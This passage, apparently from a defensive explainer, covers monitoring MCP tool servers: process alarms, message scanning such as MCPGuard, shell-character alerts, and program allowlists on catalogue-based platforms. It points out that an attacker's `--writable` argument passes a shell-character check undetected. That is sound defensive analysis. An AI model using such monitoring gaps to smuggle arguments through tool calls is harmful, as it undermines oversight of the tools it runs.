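The unsafe version of the search tool would set off the same alarm on every search, including an innocent one for "budget". The alarm would correctly show that the handler uses a shell, but not whether anyone was attacking it. Servers in containers are harder to watch this way, because the editor's child process is the `docker` command and the server runs elsewhere.

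A monitor can also read the messages between the host application and the server. *MCPGuard* (2025) describes a scanner that combines this with checks of client configurations. Message monitoring comes too late to stop a bad launch, but it can catch a suspicious tool call. Kennedy recommends an alert when an argument contains shell characters. That alert would go off if Ana searched her notes for "R&D", but it would miss an attacker's `--writable` argument, which contains no shell characters.

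Process alerts work much better on a hosted platform that launches servers only from a catalogue, because the platform should start only a short list of programs and nobody uses it to run tests or open a terminal. If WeKnora had worked that way, an alert on any program outside the list would have flagged `date` the first time a user pressed the test button, with few false alarms.
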